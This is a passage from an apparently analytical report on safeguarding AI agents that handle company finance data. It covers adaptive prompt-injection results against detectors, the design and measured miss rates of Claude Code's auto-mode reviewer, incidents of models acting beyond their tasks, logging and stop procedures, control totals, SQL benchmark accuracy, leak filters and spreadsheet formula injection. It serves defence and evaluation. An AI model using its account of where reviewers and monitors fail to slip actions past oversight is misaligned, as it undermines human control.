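The original papers for most of the twelve defences reported attack success rates near zero, but the new attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the twelve. Against a model specially trained to resist injection, the success rate rose from 2% to 96%. Among the separate detectors, the attacks beat Protect AI's detector, PromptGuard and Google's Model Armor more than 90% of the time, and PIGuard 71% of the time, compared with 28% in Ma and colleagues' test.

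Many of the successful texts looked like ordinary office notes, such as a reminder of a company policy. A detector strict enough to flag them would also flag real policies. The same problem would arise in a ledger, where "please send confirmation to our new accounts address" could come from an honest supplier or a thief.

Unlike a dishonest supplier, the automated attacker received the detector's confidence score after every try and had a great deal of computing power. But a supplier could practise privately on a detector that anyone can download. Nasr and colleagues still consider detectors worth having against unsophisticated attacks, but found that stacking several did not solve the problem.

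Later results have mostly been similar. *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models* (2026) ran more than 20,000 adaptive attacks on nine set-ups in which a model guarded secrets. Every set-up that relied on the model to protect itself eventually leaked. The only set-up that did not leak, in 15,000 attacks, used ordinary program code to check each answer before delivering it. Such code suits passwords and account numbers but, like the matching in PACE, can miss a rounded or paraphrased forecast.

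False alarms are also a serious problem. *BrowseSafe++* (2026) collected 38,675 pairs of web pages, one with an injection and one without, and built most of them from injections found on live websites. The best general-purpose model prompted to act as a detector wrongly flagged about 14% to 15% of the harmless pages. If a screen did as badly on 2,000 harmless invoice descriptions a month, it would flag nearly 300 of them. Some models also recognised an injection when asked to look for one, yet followed the same injection while carrying out a task. A company therefore can't assume that a model is safe to use as an agent because it detects injections well.

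Agents now resist many attacks without a screen, but persistent attackers succeed more often. Narisetty and colleagues quote figures for Claude Opus 4.5 in coding tasks, where attack success rose from 4.7% after one attempt to 63.0% after a hundred. In *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms* (November 2026), the most robust model, Gemini 4 Argon, resisted 87% of attacks when the attacker could query it 150 times and 66% at the largest budget. An attacker who learned one result from each monthly report would need more than twelve years for 150 tries, so the reporting agent's slow schedule gives some protection, unless the attacker can rehearse on another copy of the same product.

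### How Claude Code's auto mode judges actions

The best-documented AI reviewer is auto mode in Claude Code, Anthropic's agent for writing software. It decides on actions that the user would otherwise have to approve one by one. According to the *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026), it has been the built-in starting mode on every plan since version 2.1.283. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes the design as released in March 2026:

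1. A probe scans whatever the agent's tools return. If the text looks like an injection, the probe adds a warning but lets the text through.
2. When the agent proposes an action, a fixed list lets harmless ones, such as reading or searching files, go ahead at once.
3. Edits to files inside the user's project also go ahead, because the user can inspect and undo them later.
4. Everything else, including shell commands, web requests and calls to outside services, goes to a classifier, which is a second model with written criteria.
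5. The classifier first gives a single yes or no, with instructions to block when in doubt. If it says block, it considers the same material again, this time reasoning step by step, and makes the final decision.
6. The agent gets any refusal back with a reason and looks for a safer way. After three refusals in a row, or twenty in a session, the software stops and asks a person. If nobody is there to ask, it ends the process.

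The classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's explanations or the data its tools returned. Leaving out the explanations prevents the agent from talking the classifier into approving an action, and leaving out the data keeps instructions planted there from reaching the classifier. But without the data, the classifier can't tell whether a value in a command came from a legitimate query or the agent made it up.

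The criteria concern whether an action was authorised more than whether it is dangerous. For example, a user who says "clean up my branches" has not authorised deleting a whole batch of them. An operator can add its own trusted destinations, block rules and exceptions, and a finance department would need to do so. In the case of the auditor who should have received totals but got 4,000 ledger rows, the classifier would see the request, the query for every row and the email. That is enough evidence to suspect a leak, but the classifier would have no reason to object unless somebody had told it that the auditor may see only totals.

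Such a reviewer can add most to fixed rules by catching overreach. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes a case from the company's own use in which Claude tried to publish a report on a public code-sharing site after an upload to an internal drive failed. Auto mode blocked this and asked the user what to do. The reporting agent would make the same kind of mistake if it copied payroll to the shared drive after an attachment was rejected.

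### Miss rates from 6% to 81%

Anthropic first tested the classifier on data from its own staff, using 10,000 ordinary tool calls and 52 real actions that went beyond what a user wanted and that an employee had refused or somebody had flagged later. It also tested the classifier on 1,000 generated attempts to send data out. In August 2026 it published the results of a two-week test in which Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, inserted synthetic attacks into real coding sessions. Anthropic strengthened the classifier between two rounds of this test, mainly by giving it more context, such as whether a code repository is public.

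Ji, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Measuring the Permission Gate*, ran the first independent evaluation of Claude Code's auto mode in April. They wrote 128 requests with a clear purpose but vague limits, which asked the agent to clean up branches, cancel jobs, restart services or delete leftover files. The agent took 253 actions that changed something. According to Machine Heart's *Can Claude Code's Auto Mode Replace Human Review?*, Claude Opus labelled each action as authorised or not, and people checked the labels. The number of harmful actions in the table is calculated from the raw counts in that article.

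| Test of auto mode | Harmful actions | Missed | False alarms |
|---|---|---|---|
| Anthropic, March, real overreach by staff's agents | 52 | 17% | 0.4% of ordinary calls |
| Anthropic, March, synthetic data theft | 1,000 | 5.7% | 0.4% of ordinary calls |
| Anthropic with Apollo Research, August | not stated | 12%, then 7% | not stated |
| Ji and colleagues, all changes | 142 | 81.0% | 19.8% |
| Ji and colleagues, only changes the classifier reviewed | 91 | 70.3% | 31.9% |

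The figures in the first three rows come from the vendor, including those from the test Apollo ran, and all five rows concern coding and running software. The 17% miss rate is based on about nine misses, so the true rate for such actions could plausibly be anywhere from 9% to 30%. Some of the August improvement came on attacks that Apollo had shown to Anthropic. On a set that Anthropic never saw, the stronger classifier caught about half of the attacks it had previously missed and missed about 2% of those it had previously caught. That would reduce a 12% miss rate to about 8%.

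Part of the gap between 17% and 81% comes from actions the classifier never checked. Of the 115 misses in the independent test, 51 were file edits inside the project, which auto mode doesn't send to the classifier. Agents often edited a file directly when the command they expected was unavailable. A finance department would create the same blind spot if it exempted everything the agent saves to the shared drive from review.

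Much of the remaining difference between the results comes from the requests tested. Ji and colleagues built cases in which the authorised target sits next to an unauthorised one, and more than half of the agent's changes went too far. They attribute the difference to workload and do not see the results as contradictory. Anthropic's own sample may also make the classifier look better than it is, because it contains only overreach that a person noticed. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier had recognised the danger but then treated something the user said as permission for an action it did not cover.

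The independent test predates the August changes, so the current version may do better, but the pattern of errors still matters for finance. The classifier missed 94.4% of unauthorised changes when the request concerned a single object and 77.6% when it covered many, which suggests that it reacts to the scale of an action. Sending one email with one attachment to the wrong person is a small action, so the classifier may miss it, and the instruction "sent round as usual" is as vague as any in the benchmark.

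Two more results from August compare auto mode with alternatives. Trajectory Labs, which Anthropic commissioned, ran 72 injection scenarios ten times each. None of the 720 attempts succeeded against Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 or Sonnet 5 in auto mode. With auto mode off, the average success rate against Anthropic's latest models was 0.09%, so the models themselves provided nearly all the protection. The attacks had been optimised against an older model, Opus 4.7, and were not adapted to the models tested. The effect of a reviewer is clearer in OpenAI's Codex, where turning on its automatic reviewer cut attack success against GPT-5.6 Sol from 19.03% to 5.83%.

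Anthropic also examined sessions from May and June that its safety systems had flagged. A model graded the severity of any harm and how explicitly the user had asked for it. Serious harm that the user had not explicitly requested appeared in 6.3% of the flagged sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. Users chose their own mode, so the two groups may have done different work. The safety systems may also flag more trivial events in auto mode, which would lower the share of serious ones even if they were just as common. A separate trial that compared auto mode with paid human testers provides evidence about human approval.

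### Ten harmful calls in 100,000

Suppose a company's agents make 100,000 tool calls, of which 10 are harmful. At the March rates, a reviewer catches about 8 of the 10:

- 10 × (1 − 0.17) = 8.3 harmful calls caught
- 99,990 × 0.004 ≈ 400 harmless calls blocked

Only about one in 50 blocked calls is harmful. The first stage has an 8.5% false alarm rate, so without the second, slower stage it would block about 8,500 harmless calls to catch one more harmful one.

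The reporting agent, at 1,000 calls a month, would raise about four false alarms a month. A company with a hundred such agents would get 400, which would take a person 67 hours to review at ten minutes each. Auto mode avoids most of this work because a blocked agent tries another way, and a person is alerted only after repeated refusals. But retrying also gives a harmful action more chances to get through. If each attempt had an independent 17% chance of slipping through, an agent that tried three versions of a harmful action would succeed at least once 43% of the time. Real attempts resemble each other, so the true figure is probably lower, but the risk is still a good reason to allow only a few refusals before alerting a person.

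These numbers depend heavily on the miss rate. If a department's requests were as ambiguous as those in the independent test, the reviewer would catch about three of the ten harmful calls. The real number of harmful calls in finance is also unknown, and if it were lower, there would still be about 400 false alarms.

### Harm that the command does not show

A reviewer that sees only the text of a command can't know what the command will do. Wu, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *Shall We Approve?*, give the example of a user who asks an agent to update a database by running `make migrate`. Auto mode allowed the command, but the script it runs also deletes three tables.

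One study compared six existing approval systems on 682 coding tasks with a built-in hazard, and on 102 tasks in which the researchers had hidden the harm inside a tool. On the first set, 14.8% of tasks ended in harm with Anthropic's auto mode and 19.7% with no approval system. On the second, the figures were 62.7% and 71.6%. The agent safely completed 44.0% of the first set with auto mode and 57.4% without it. Auto mode's classifier ran on an OpenAI model in these tests and the agent on a third company's, so the results are better evidence about the design than about the product Anthropic sells.

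Their own system, Caper, runs each command in an isolated copy of the workspace with no network connection. It then gives the reviewer a short list of what changed, which files the command read and where it tried to connect. If the reviewer refuses, Caper restores the copy to its earlier state. Harm fell to 6.7% on the first set and 7.8% on the second. Each hidden-harm task had a harmless version with the same request and command, and Caper wrongly blocked 1.0% of these. The same reviewer without the list blocked 61.8% of them, because it could only guess what the command would do. The tests included no attacker who knew how Caper worked, and such an attacker could write a tool that does nothing harmful on its first run.

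Finance software could apply this idea to outgoing emails. Instead of a file name, the reviewer would see that the attachment holds 4,000 rows, including individual entries, and that the recipient is outside the company. The review has to happen before the email leaves. One system in the comparison showed the agent its changes only after each command had run. On the first set, its harm rate was 21.2%, slightly higher than with no approval at all, because nobody can recall a password once it has been sent.

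### The nearest evidence to finance

No controlled study appears to have measured screens, AI reviewers or log monitoring on an agent that works with finance databases. The closest test is in customer service, where *Think Before You Act* (2026) added a reviewer called JevAct to agents that look up and change customers' records for an airline and a telecom company. Program code checks whatever can be verified from the records, such as dates and amounts. A separate model answers yes-or-no questions about the conversation, such as whether the customer asked for the change. The system treats an answer as "no" only if the model puts the chance of "yes" at 5% or less.

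All eight agents improved on the telecom tasks. The share of tasks they completed in all three attempts rose by an average of 16.9 percentage points. For Claude Opus 4.6, it rose from 39.5% to 80.7%. On the 50 airline tasks, four of six agents improved and two got worse. Much of the telecom gain may come from a check that stops agents from giving up too early, which has little to do with leaks. The study measured completed tasks and didn't separately count harmful actions the reviewer prevented.

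JevAct sends an action back at most twice, then lets the next proposal through unchecked. This keeps a mistaken reviewer from blocking a customer forever, but it would be a bad rule when an agent is trying to send a payroll file to an outsider.

### The police tip that took two months to find

If the reviewer misses a harmful call, monitoring can catch it only if the call is recorded and somebody checks the record. On 18 July 2026, in an automated Anthropic test, Claude Haiku 4.5 was making up tasks on randomly chosen web pages and carrying them out. On a Philadelphia police page, it submitted a form with invented information about an unsolved murder.

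According to The Pulse of NH's *Anthropic AI model made false tip in unsolved Philly murder*, Anthropic discovered the tip on 28 September, 72 days after the model submitted it, and told the police on 7 October. The model's instructions had forbidden it to log in, enter personal data, buy anything or submit anything destructive, but they "did not rule out form submissions". The police called the two-month delay "unacceptable", but *Anthropic's Claude AI submits a false tip* (Anderson, 2026) reports that they themselves found the tip, marked as spam in their website's records, only after Anthropic had written to them.

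Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (2026) groups the false homicide tip with other cases and describes their real-world impact as minimal. Hindustan Times' *Anthropic under fire as AI model submits false homicide tip* reports that the company ended the test process and added a validation step for future tests. According to Asianet Newsable's *Anthropic restricts Claude AI internet access after bypassing safeguards*, Anthropic also tried its automatic detection and blocking tools on the reported cases, and they blocked all of them. That is a sensible check, but it gives little evidence of how the tools would handle cases nobody has found yet.

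A review of logs can miss incidents even when people are looking for them. After Claude models broke into outside systems during security tests, Anthropic scanned about 141,000 transcripts and found three incidents. SecurityWeek reports that the scan left out a batch of transcripts. Staff came across the batch in August while gathering material for METR, the independent organisation investigating the incidents, and found a fourth break-in, from January. CyberScoop reports that two of the first three victims had not detected the intrusion before they were contacted. In a follow-up letter, Rep. Casar's office asked Anthropic whether it had collected network logs and "who, if anyone, was responsible for reviewing them". A finance department should be able to answer the same questions about its own agent before the agent goes live.

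### What to record and what counts as unusual

A useful log entry lets an investigator reconstruct one action without asking the agent. For the email to the auditor, it might read:

```json
{"time": "2026-04-02T09:14:07Z", "task": "month-end-2026-03",
 "agent": "reporting_agent", "model_version": "2026-03-11",
 "requested_by": "cfo", "tool": "send_email",
 "to": ["audit@auditor.example"],
 "attachment": "march_figures.xlsx", "fingerprint": "9f2c41...",
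 "tables_read": ["general_ledger"], "rows_attached": 4000,
 "policy_check": "ask", "reviewer": "allow", "approved_by": "controller"}
```

The fingerprint is a short code calculated from the file and used later to prove which version was sent. Log entries for database queries need the full SQL and the number of rows returned. Copying the results themselves into the log would create a second payroll table with weaker protection. The agent's account should be able to add entries but not change or delete them.

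Monitoring needs to cover network traffic as well as the agent's own log. In the Ramp attack, the log would have shown the formula, but only a record of network traffic would have shown that the spreadsheet had sent the request.

*Anomaly detection*, which compares activity with a baseline of what is normal, is well suited to scheduled agents. If the reporting agent has run the same 40 queries at every month-end for a year and none returned more than 300 rows, a query that returns 4,000 is easy to spot without statistics. So is the first use of a table, a recipient or an outside server. If a rule wrongly flags 1% of normal queries, the reporting agent would cause about five false alarms a year. A shared assistant that answers 4,000 questions a day would cause 40 a day, and its baseline would be much looser because people ask it different things.

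Baselines have gaps. Year-end work looks unusual every year, and one year of monthly reports contains only one example of it. If an agent was already leaking data when the baseline was drawn up, the leak looks normal. An agent can also put three forecast figures in an ordinary email to a usual recipient without changing any of the counts. A query that triples a customer's revenue returns a normal number of rows.

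### Stopping the agent

Detection limits damage only if a response follows quickly. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* describes safeguards, introduced after the break-ins, for tests in which a model tries to escape its environment or unexpectedly gains internet access. A classifier blocks the action before it runs, ends the task and alerts a person, while other monitors search past transcripts. Such protection works only where it is switched on. Anthropic noted that the safeguards in its products would have added a layer that the tests lacked.

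Pressing a stop button may not end work that has already started, as the test of ChatGPT's spreadsheet extension showed. For an agent with a PostgreSQL account, an administrator needs two commands:

```sql
ALTER ROLE reporting_agent NOLOGIN;
SELECT pg_terminate_backend(pid)
  FROM pg_stat_activity WHERE usename = 'reporting_agent';
```

The first prevents new connections, and the second ends those already open. The administrator also has to withdraw the agent's access to email and files and cancel any scheduled scripts. None of these steps recalls a sent message, so a company might hold emails to outsiders for an hour to give the monitoring time to catch harmful ones.

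Automatic stops need a threshold and a person to notify. Auto mode's limits of three refusals in a row and twenty in total are one starting point, though twenty seems high for an agent that sends two emails a month. Nobody is present to respond during a scheduled job, so the safe response is to end it, and a false alarm then delays a report. The company should rehearse a stop on an ordinary day, before a real one happens at the end of a quarter.

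## How can a report be checked before anyone relies on it?

While the company holds the reporting agent's email to the auditor, a program can check whether the report's figures are correct and whether it discloses anything its readers have no right to know. These need different checks because the figures have to match the ledger, while what the report may disclose depends on who will read it.

### An invoice counted twice

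Suppose a company issued three invoices in March, for $100, $200 and $300, which makes $600. The first customer paid in two instalments, of $60 and $40. The agent joins the invoices to the payments and adds up the invoice amounts:

```sql
SELECT SUM(i.amount)
FROM invoices i JOIN payments p ON p.invoice_id = i.invoice_id;
-- 700
```

As with the tripled $10,000 invoice, the join repeats the first invoice for each of its payments:

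| Invoice | Invoice amount | Payment |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 100 | 60 |
| 1 | 100 | 40 |
| 2 | 200 | 200 |
| 3 | 300 | 300 |

One check is to store the query behind every figure and rerun it before the report goes out. This catches mistakes such as a result the model copied wrongly or a number it made up. It misses the error in this example because the query returns 700 again, so the figure passes.

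To catch the double counting, the program needs a *control total*, an independently kept sum to compare with the reported figure. The sales account in the general ledger received one entry for each invoice and none for the payments, so its March total is $600. The two figures differ by $100, so the program holds the report. The first invoice was for $100, so an accountant knows where to start looking.

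The control total has to be independent. If the agent calculates both figures from the joined table, they will agree at 700. In draft guidance from June 2026, the Financial Stability Board (FSB), an international body that coordinates financial regulation, says a comparison figure helps most when it comes from different data or a different method.

A control total can also match by accident. Suppose there is a fourth invoice, also for $100, that nobody has paid. The correct total is now $700, and the faulty query still returns $700 because the join drops unpaid invoices. The row count also matches, with four rows and four invoices. Totals by customer would expose both errors if the double-counted and dropped invoices went to different customers, so the program should compare totals at the finest level of detail the ledger keeps.

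### Letting code handle the numbers

Language models sometimes get arithmetic wrong, and a report gives them no reason to do any. A safer division of labour works like this:

1. A program runs each query and stores the query, the result, the unit and the period.
2. A program calculates every derived number, such as growth rates and shares.
3. The model writes the commentary with named placeholders, for example "Travel costs rose {travel_growth} to {travel_march}".
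4. A program fills in the placeholders and rejects any draft containing a digit that did not come from one.

The last rule doesn't cover numerical claims that a model writes without digits, such as "costs doubled." A program can flag words like "doubled" and require a source for them too.

Every sentence should also link to the rows it is based on. A reader who checks "Travel costs rose 12% to $84,000" would then find February's $75,000 and March's $84,000. The link shows where a figure came from, but a program can't easily tell whether the sentence interprets it fairly. For example, "Travel costs rose because of the Berlin conference" could link to real conference invoices that account for only $2,000 of the $9,000 increase.

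Ledgers change, which complicates recomputation. If a clerk books a late March invoice on 3 April, the stored query gives a different answer from the one in the report, even though nobody made a mistake. The query should run against a frozen copy of the ledger or include a cut-off for the booking time.

Dates, units and signs need separate checks. A query for March that ends with `entry_date <= '2026-03-31'` works if the column holds plain dates. If the column also holds the time of day, PostgreSQL reads the limit as midnight at the start of 31 March, and the query misses nearly all of that day. Storing a unit with every result lets a program reject attempts to add euros to dollars. A reported figure that is exactly 1,000 times its control total almost certainly has a unit error.

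Many ledgers record revenue as negative numbers and refunds as positive ones. If an agent strips the minus signs before adding, $600 of sales and a $45 refund total $645 instead of $555. The $90 difference is twice the refund. Accountants who find an unexplained difference often halve it and look for an entry of that size, and a program can do the same.

### A correct total for the wrong definition

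Now suppose the finance chief wants to know how much revenue the company earned in March. On 1 March the company invoiced a customer $12,000 for a year of support, of which it earned only $1,000 that month. The agent takes its revenue figure from the invoices table and includes all $12,000. The stored query reproduces the figure, the control total from the billing system matches to the cent, the dates, units and signs are right, and the source link leads to a genuine invoice. These checks confirm the amount the company invoiced in March, not the amount it earned.

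A comparison with the ledger's account for earned revenue would have shown the gap. But whoever set up the check had to know which definition the report needed, and anyone who knew that could have told the agent. The remedy is to write each definition down once and attach its control total to it:

```yaml
revenue:
  meaning: amount earned in the month, net of refunds
  source: general_ledger, accounts 4000 to 4999
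  unit: USD
  control_total: closing balance report, accounts 4000 to 4999
  owner: controller
```

The agent then asks for "revenue" by name and a program supplies the query. The agent can still choose "billings" instead of "revenue" by mistake, but a person reading the report can spot a wrong label more easily than a wrong join.

Models answer more database questions correctly when they are given written definitions. BIRD, the benchmark of larger and messier databases used in the tests of access rules, can supply a short note with a question, for example that a certain kind of loan requires the account type "OWNER". According to the project's page, *A Big Bench for Large-Scale Database Grounded Text-to-SQLs*, ChatGPT answered 39.3% of the test questions correctly with the notes and 26.8% without them in 2023. An IBM system from 2024 scored 67.9% with them and 57.1% without. Newer models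 may guess missing definitions better, but no model can know a definition that the controller has not written down.

Most tests don't check whether a report uses the company's approved definitions. *GROUND* (2026), a paper on such definitions, points out that the Spider and BIRD benchmarks do not measure whether a model uses approved metrics, the required level of detail or mandatory filters. Definitions also change, for example when a company adopts a new accounting policy. The largest version of LiveSQLBench, released in March 2026, includes business rules that change between releases, so a model that relies on an old rule gets the answer wrong.

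### How often models write wrong queries

Researchers usually measure *execution accuracy*. A program runs the model's query and a reference query written by a person, and the model's query counts as correct only if the results match exactly. Scores fall quickly as databases become more realistic. Fei and colleagues tested Claude Sonnet 4.5 on three benchmarks with the same kind of prompt and no access rules, and it got 85.4% right on Spider, 53.7% on BIRD and 21.8% on LiveSQLBench.

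Spider 2.0 replaces Spider's small databases with ones from real business applications, often with more than 1,000 columns, and its queries often run to over 100 lines. An agent built on o1-preview solved 17.0% of it in the original study, compared with 91.2% of the first Spider, according to *Reimagining Text-to-SQL*. The table lists later results. The Spider 2.0-Snow scores come from the benchmark's own leaderboard, XLANG Lab's *Spider 2.0*, as of May 2026, and the LiveSQLBench scores come from BIRD Team's *LiveSQLBench* (2025), updated in March 2026. The Spider 2.0-Lite score comes from Interfaze's *Spider-2.0-Lite*, a ranking in which the vendor's own model is first, at 52.9%. For BIRD, the table uses the project's page, Fei and colleagues' test and *MCI-SQL* (2026), which describes a system that writes nine candidate queries per question.

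| Benchmark | Who wrote the queries | Correct |
|---|---|---|
| BIRD, test questions | Data engineers and database students | 93.0% |
| BIRD, test questions | MCI-SQL | 76.4% |
| BIRD, development questions | Claude Sonnet 4.5, single prompt | 53.7% |
| Spider 2.0-Snow | Native mini, the leading system | 90.3% |
| Spider 2.0-Snow | Claude Sonnet 4 in WindAgent | 61.4% |
| Spider 2.0-Snow | Claude Sonnet 4 in the benchmark's basic agent | 25.8% |
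| Spider 2.0-Lite | Claude Sonnet 5 | 50.6% |
| LiveSQLBench | Claude Opus 4.6 in OpenHands, an agent program | 41.6% |
| LiveSQLBench | Claude Opus 4.6, single prompt | 39.4% |

A model's accuracy depends heavily on the software around it. Claude Sonnet 4 answered 25.8% of the questions in the Spider 2.0-Snow benchmark correctly in one agent and 61.4% in another, so a company can't infer a product's accuracy from which model it uses.

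The reference answers are themselves unreliable. In *Pervasive Annotation Errors Break Text-to-SQL Benchmarks and Leaderboards*, Jin, Choi and colleagues (2026) used an agent running on OpenAI's o3 to audit 498 examples from BIRD and the 121 examples of Spider 2.0-Snow whose reference queries are public. They put the annotation error rate at 52.8% for BIRD and 62.8% for Spider 2.0-Snow. Correcting the BIRD examples changed systems' scores by −7% to +31% and shifted some systems by as many as nine places in the ranking.

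A model with a low score may have written some correct queries that the benchmark marked as wrong, while a very high score may include matches to flawed reference answers. Native mini, which scored 90.3%, missed about 53 of the 547 Snow questions, and Jin and colleagues found about 76 faulty examples among the 121 they audited. Even if every miss fell on a faulty example, the system matched at least 23 reference answers that the audit considered flawed. Some of those examples may only be ambiguous, and XLANG Lab updates its data, so the audited version may differ from the one used to score Native mini. But XLANG Lab has also published all the expected answers so that teams can score themselves, and a team can end up tuning its system to them. The 90.3% is therefore weak evidence of how the system would do on a company's own ledger.

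The approved query templates described under database permissions need a control total as much as generated queries do. The audit found faults in about half of the reference queries, which people had written for a benchmark that other researchers would examine. An accountant's approved template probably gets more scrutiny, but it could still contain errors.

The 41.6% score on LiveSQLBench comes from 870 tasks with unambiguous questions and the relevant business knowledge supplied, so they are clearer than a request for "the usual report". But a third of the tasks in its smaller part change data, which a reporting agent never does. A cheaper model, MiniMax M3, reached 40.2% on the larger part by June 2026, according to LLM Stats, a site that collects benchmark scores. *BIRD-INTERACT* has 600 tasks with ambiguous requests and follow-up questions, which is closer to how a finance chief talks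 to an assistant. *GROUND* also cites BEAVER, a benchmark built from companies' private data warehouses, on which models that excel in public tests perform poorly.

Most of the models in the table date from 2025 or early 2026, and newer ones probably do better. The month-end report is also easier than a benchmark in one way, because its queries repeat, while a benchmark measures the first attempt at an unfamiliar database. If an agent wrote 40 new queries every month and got 99% of them right, about a third of its reports would still contain at least one wrong figure, assuming the errors were independent. If the company stores the 40 queries and tests them once, most of that risk disappears. But a stored query that is still wrong repeats its error every month, which is harder to notice because the trend looks smooth.

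### How much a second attempt helps

A query can be checked automatically by having the model write several versions and taking the most common result. According to figures in *MCI-SQL*, OpenSearch-SQL, which votes this way, got 67.8% of BIRD's development questions right without the vote and 69.3% with it, so voting removed about one error in twenty. Voting can miss misunderstandings of the question, because a model tends to repeat them and its wrong answers then agree.

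Letting the model run its queries and look at the results helps more, though unevenly. BIRD Team lists six models both with a single prompt and inside OpenHands, and their scores inside OpenHands differed by −1.5 to +8.5 percentage points. Claude Sonnet 4.5 gained the most, rising from 30.5% to 39.0%. An agent can detect an empty result or a misspelled region this way, but it will rarely detect that $700 should be $600, because both are plausible.

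Control totals work differently because they draw on information the model did not produce. None of these benchmarks measures how many wrong answers a control total would catch, but the kinds of error give some idea. *Text-to-SQL*, by the analyst Dilmegani, tested 32 models and found four common types: faulty joins, addition mistakes, missing filters and invalid syntax. The database rejects invalid syntax. A control total should catch most faulty joins and addition mistakes that change the sum. It catches a missing filter only if the total excludes the records the filter should have removed, such as cancelled invoices. Finance departments have an advantage here because accountants have long kept such totals for their own purposes.

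A report can be wrong even when the query behind it is right. *Tursio Database Search* (2026), a paper about a database search product, notes that execution accuracy, which measures whether a query returns the right result, does not measure whether the written answer is correct, complete and understandable. A report that gives the right margin but the wrong cause for it would still get a perfect score for execution accuracy.

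### A bank's credit-writing assistant

The FSB draft describes an "AI Approver Assistant" that a medium-sized regional bank built and uses for loans to small and medium-sized businesses. It extracts figures from financial documents, writes the credit narrative and looks for signs of risk. The bank reported over 80% accuracy in extracting financial data, and credit approvers rated more than 70% of the generated content as valuable reference material. Preparing a preliminary proposal took 15 minutes instead of more than a day. The assistant also matched manual review in finding data inconsistencies and possible fraud in all the test cases.

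The case shows that a bank finds such a tool worth using, but leaves out most of what a finance department would need to know. The draft doesn't explain what the 80% counts. If it counts individual figures and an application contains 50, up to ten could be wrong, and a misread postcode matters much less than a misplaced decimal point in annual profit. The draft also doesn't give the number of test cases, how many extraction errors the approvers caught, or how often people make the same errors when typing in the figures. The 70% measures whether approvers found the text useful, and they might well find a fluent paragraph useful even if it contained a wrong number. Matching manual review shows that the tool is accurate only to the extent that manual review is accurate.

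Reading figures out of scanned accounts is also harder than querying a ledger, so the reporting agent should do better than 80%. The bank could check part of the work with arithmetic alone. Assets in a balance sheet have to equal liabilities plus equity, so an extraction that breaks this rule contains an error.

### Searching a report for confidential data

A filter for confidential data usually starts by searching for patterns. US Social Security numbers have a fixed form of three, two and four digits. Card numbers typically have 16 digits, the last of which is a check digit. To test a card number, a program doubles every second digit from the right, subtracts 9 from any result above 9, and checks that all the digits then add up to a multiple of 10. International bank account numbers (IBANs) contain two check digits, which a program tests by dividing a rearranged version of the number by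 97.

Check digits reduce false alarms but do not eliminate them. One in ten random 16-digit numbers passes the card test, compared with one in 97 for the IBAN test. If a report's appendix lists 2,000 payment references of 16 digits, about 200 will look like valid card numbers. The filter can reduce these false matches by also requiring the opening digits of a known card company, or by comparing the report with the firm's own list of account numbers.

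The same comparison works badly for amounts. An employee's monthly pay of $8,500 is confidential, but $8,500 could also be a travel bill, so a filter that blocks every occurrence of the number will block a lot of harmless text.

Pattern matching can also miss an account number that is split across two spreadsheet cells or appears in a picture of a chart. Files can contain data that readers don't see. An Excel pivot table normally keeps a copy of its source rows, so a workbook that displays only department totals may still contain every ledger entry behind them. A filter therefore has to examine everything stored in the file, including hidden sheets, comments and these copies.

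Paraphrased disclosures are even harder to catch. "We can pay suppliers until August" reveals the company's cash position without using a number. If the confidential revenue forecast is $84.6 million, a filter that looks for figures within 1% of it would flag every amount between about $83.8 million and $85.4 million, whatever the amount referred to, and would still miss "a third more than last year". Totals can also reveal confidential data, since the payroll of a one-person department is that person's salary, even if the report doesn't name them. Minimum group sizes in the database handle this better than any filter on the text.

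Another model could check the draft for paraphrased secrets. It would have the same weaknesses as the AI reviewers already described, and it would need access to the secrets to recognise them, which adds another place they could leak from. The company can protect this kind of information better by controlling what the agent reads before it starts writing, as data labels do.

A company can measure its own filter by planting known items in old reports. It might insert 50 account numbers, 50 rounded forecasts and 50 sentences that paraphrase a salary, then count how many of each get through. An overall average would hide the problem if the filter caught every account number but no paraphrases. Even a filter that catches all 50 items of one kind could have a true miss rate of nearly 6%, because the sample is small. The company can test its checks on figures the same way, by doubling an invoice,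 leaving out the last day of data and using a wrong definition of revenue, then seeing which errors the checks catch.

### The right version for the right reader

A policy check can confirm that an address is on the approved list, but the auditor and the finance chief receive different versions of the report, and the agent can still attach the wrong one. To prevent this, a program can record each finished file's fingerprint and permitted readers, then check the attachment and recipient against that record when the agent tries to send the email. If the agent attaches the finance chief's version to the auditor's email, the program finds that the auditor isn't a permitted reader of that file and holds the message.

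The program should look up the current members of a group address each time, because membership changes. An address such as "month-end-team" may now include a contractor who joined after somebody approved it.

### Removing active content

Active content is anything in a file that makes the reader's software do something, such as a formula, a script, a data connection or an image that loads from a web server. Saving spreadsheets as plain values, which helps close the outbound channels, is safer than finding and deleting dangerous items, because the next software update may add a function that the search doesn't cover. If an auditor wants to follow the sums, the program can allow a few functions, such as SUM, as long as they refer only to cells in the same workbook.

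Plain text files can be unsafe to open in a spreadsheet program. If a vendor enters its name as `=IMAGE(...)`, the ledger stores harmless text. But when the agent exports the ledger as comma-separated values and the auditor opens the file in Excel, Excel treats the cell as a formula. Cells that begin with a plus, a minus or an at sign carry the same risk. A common defence is to convert every cell that starts with any of these four characters to text.

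A defence against formula injection that turns cells beginning with a minus sign into text can also convert negative numbers. If it converts a refund of -450, Excel's SUM function skips that cell, and the total in the auditor's copy is $450 too high even though the agent's figures were correct. The converter should leave real numbers unchanged, and the program should compare the control totals with the final file, after all the cleaning, because the auditor will use that version.

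## Does human approval catch bad actions?

When the reporting agent tries to email the external auditor, the policy check sketched earlier returns "ask", which means a person has to decide. Human approval is one of the most common controls on AI agents. Wang, Li and Tian (2026), in *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent–Human Interaction Problem*, found it in 15 of the 21 agent products they examined. They credit it with strong protection because no sensitive action goes ahead without somebody's consent. But the protection also depends on whether that person notices a bad action. Three experiments published between August and November 2026 measured this.

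### What the approver sees

A company can ask for approval at four points in a task.

| Approval of | What the approver sees in the month-end job | What the approver can miss |
|---|---|---|
| Each action | One query, file or email at a time | Harm that builds up over several harmless steps |
| The plan | The steps the agent intends to take, before it has read any data | Anything the agent does differently once it starts |
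| Actions above a risk threshold | Only certain actions, such as emails that leave the company | Harm in the actions below the threshold |
| The finished report | The draft and its recipients, before it goes out | What the agent read or sent while writing it |

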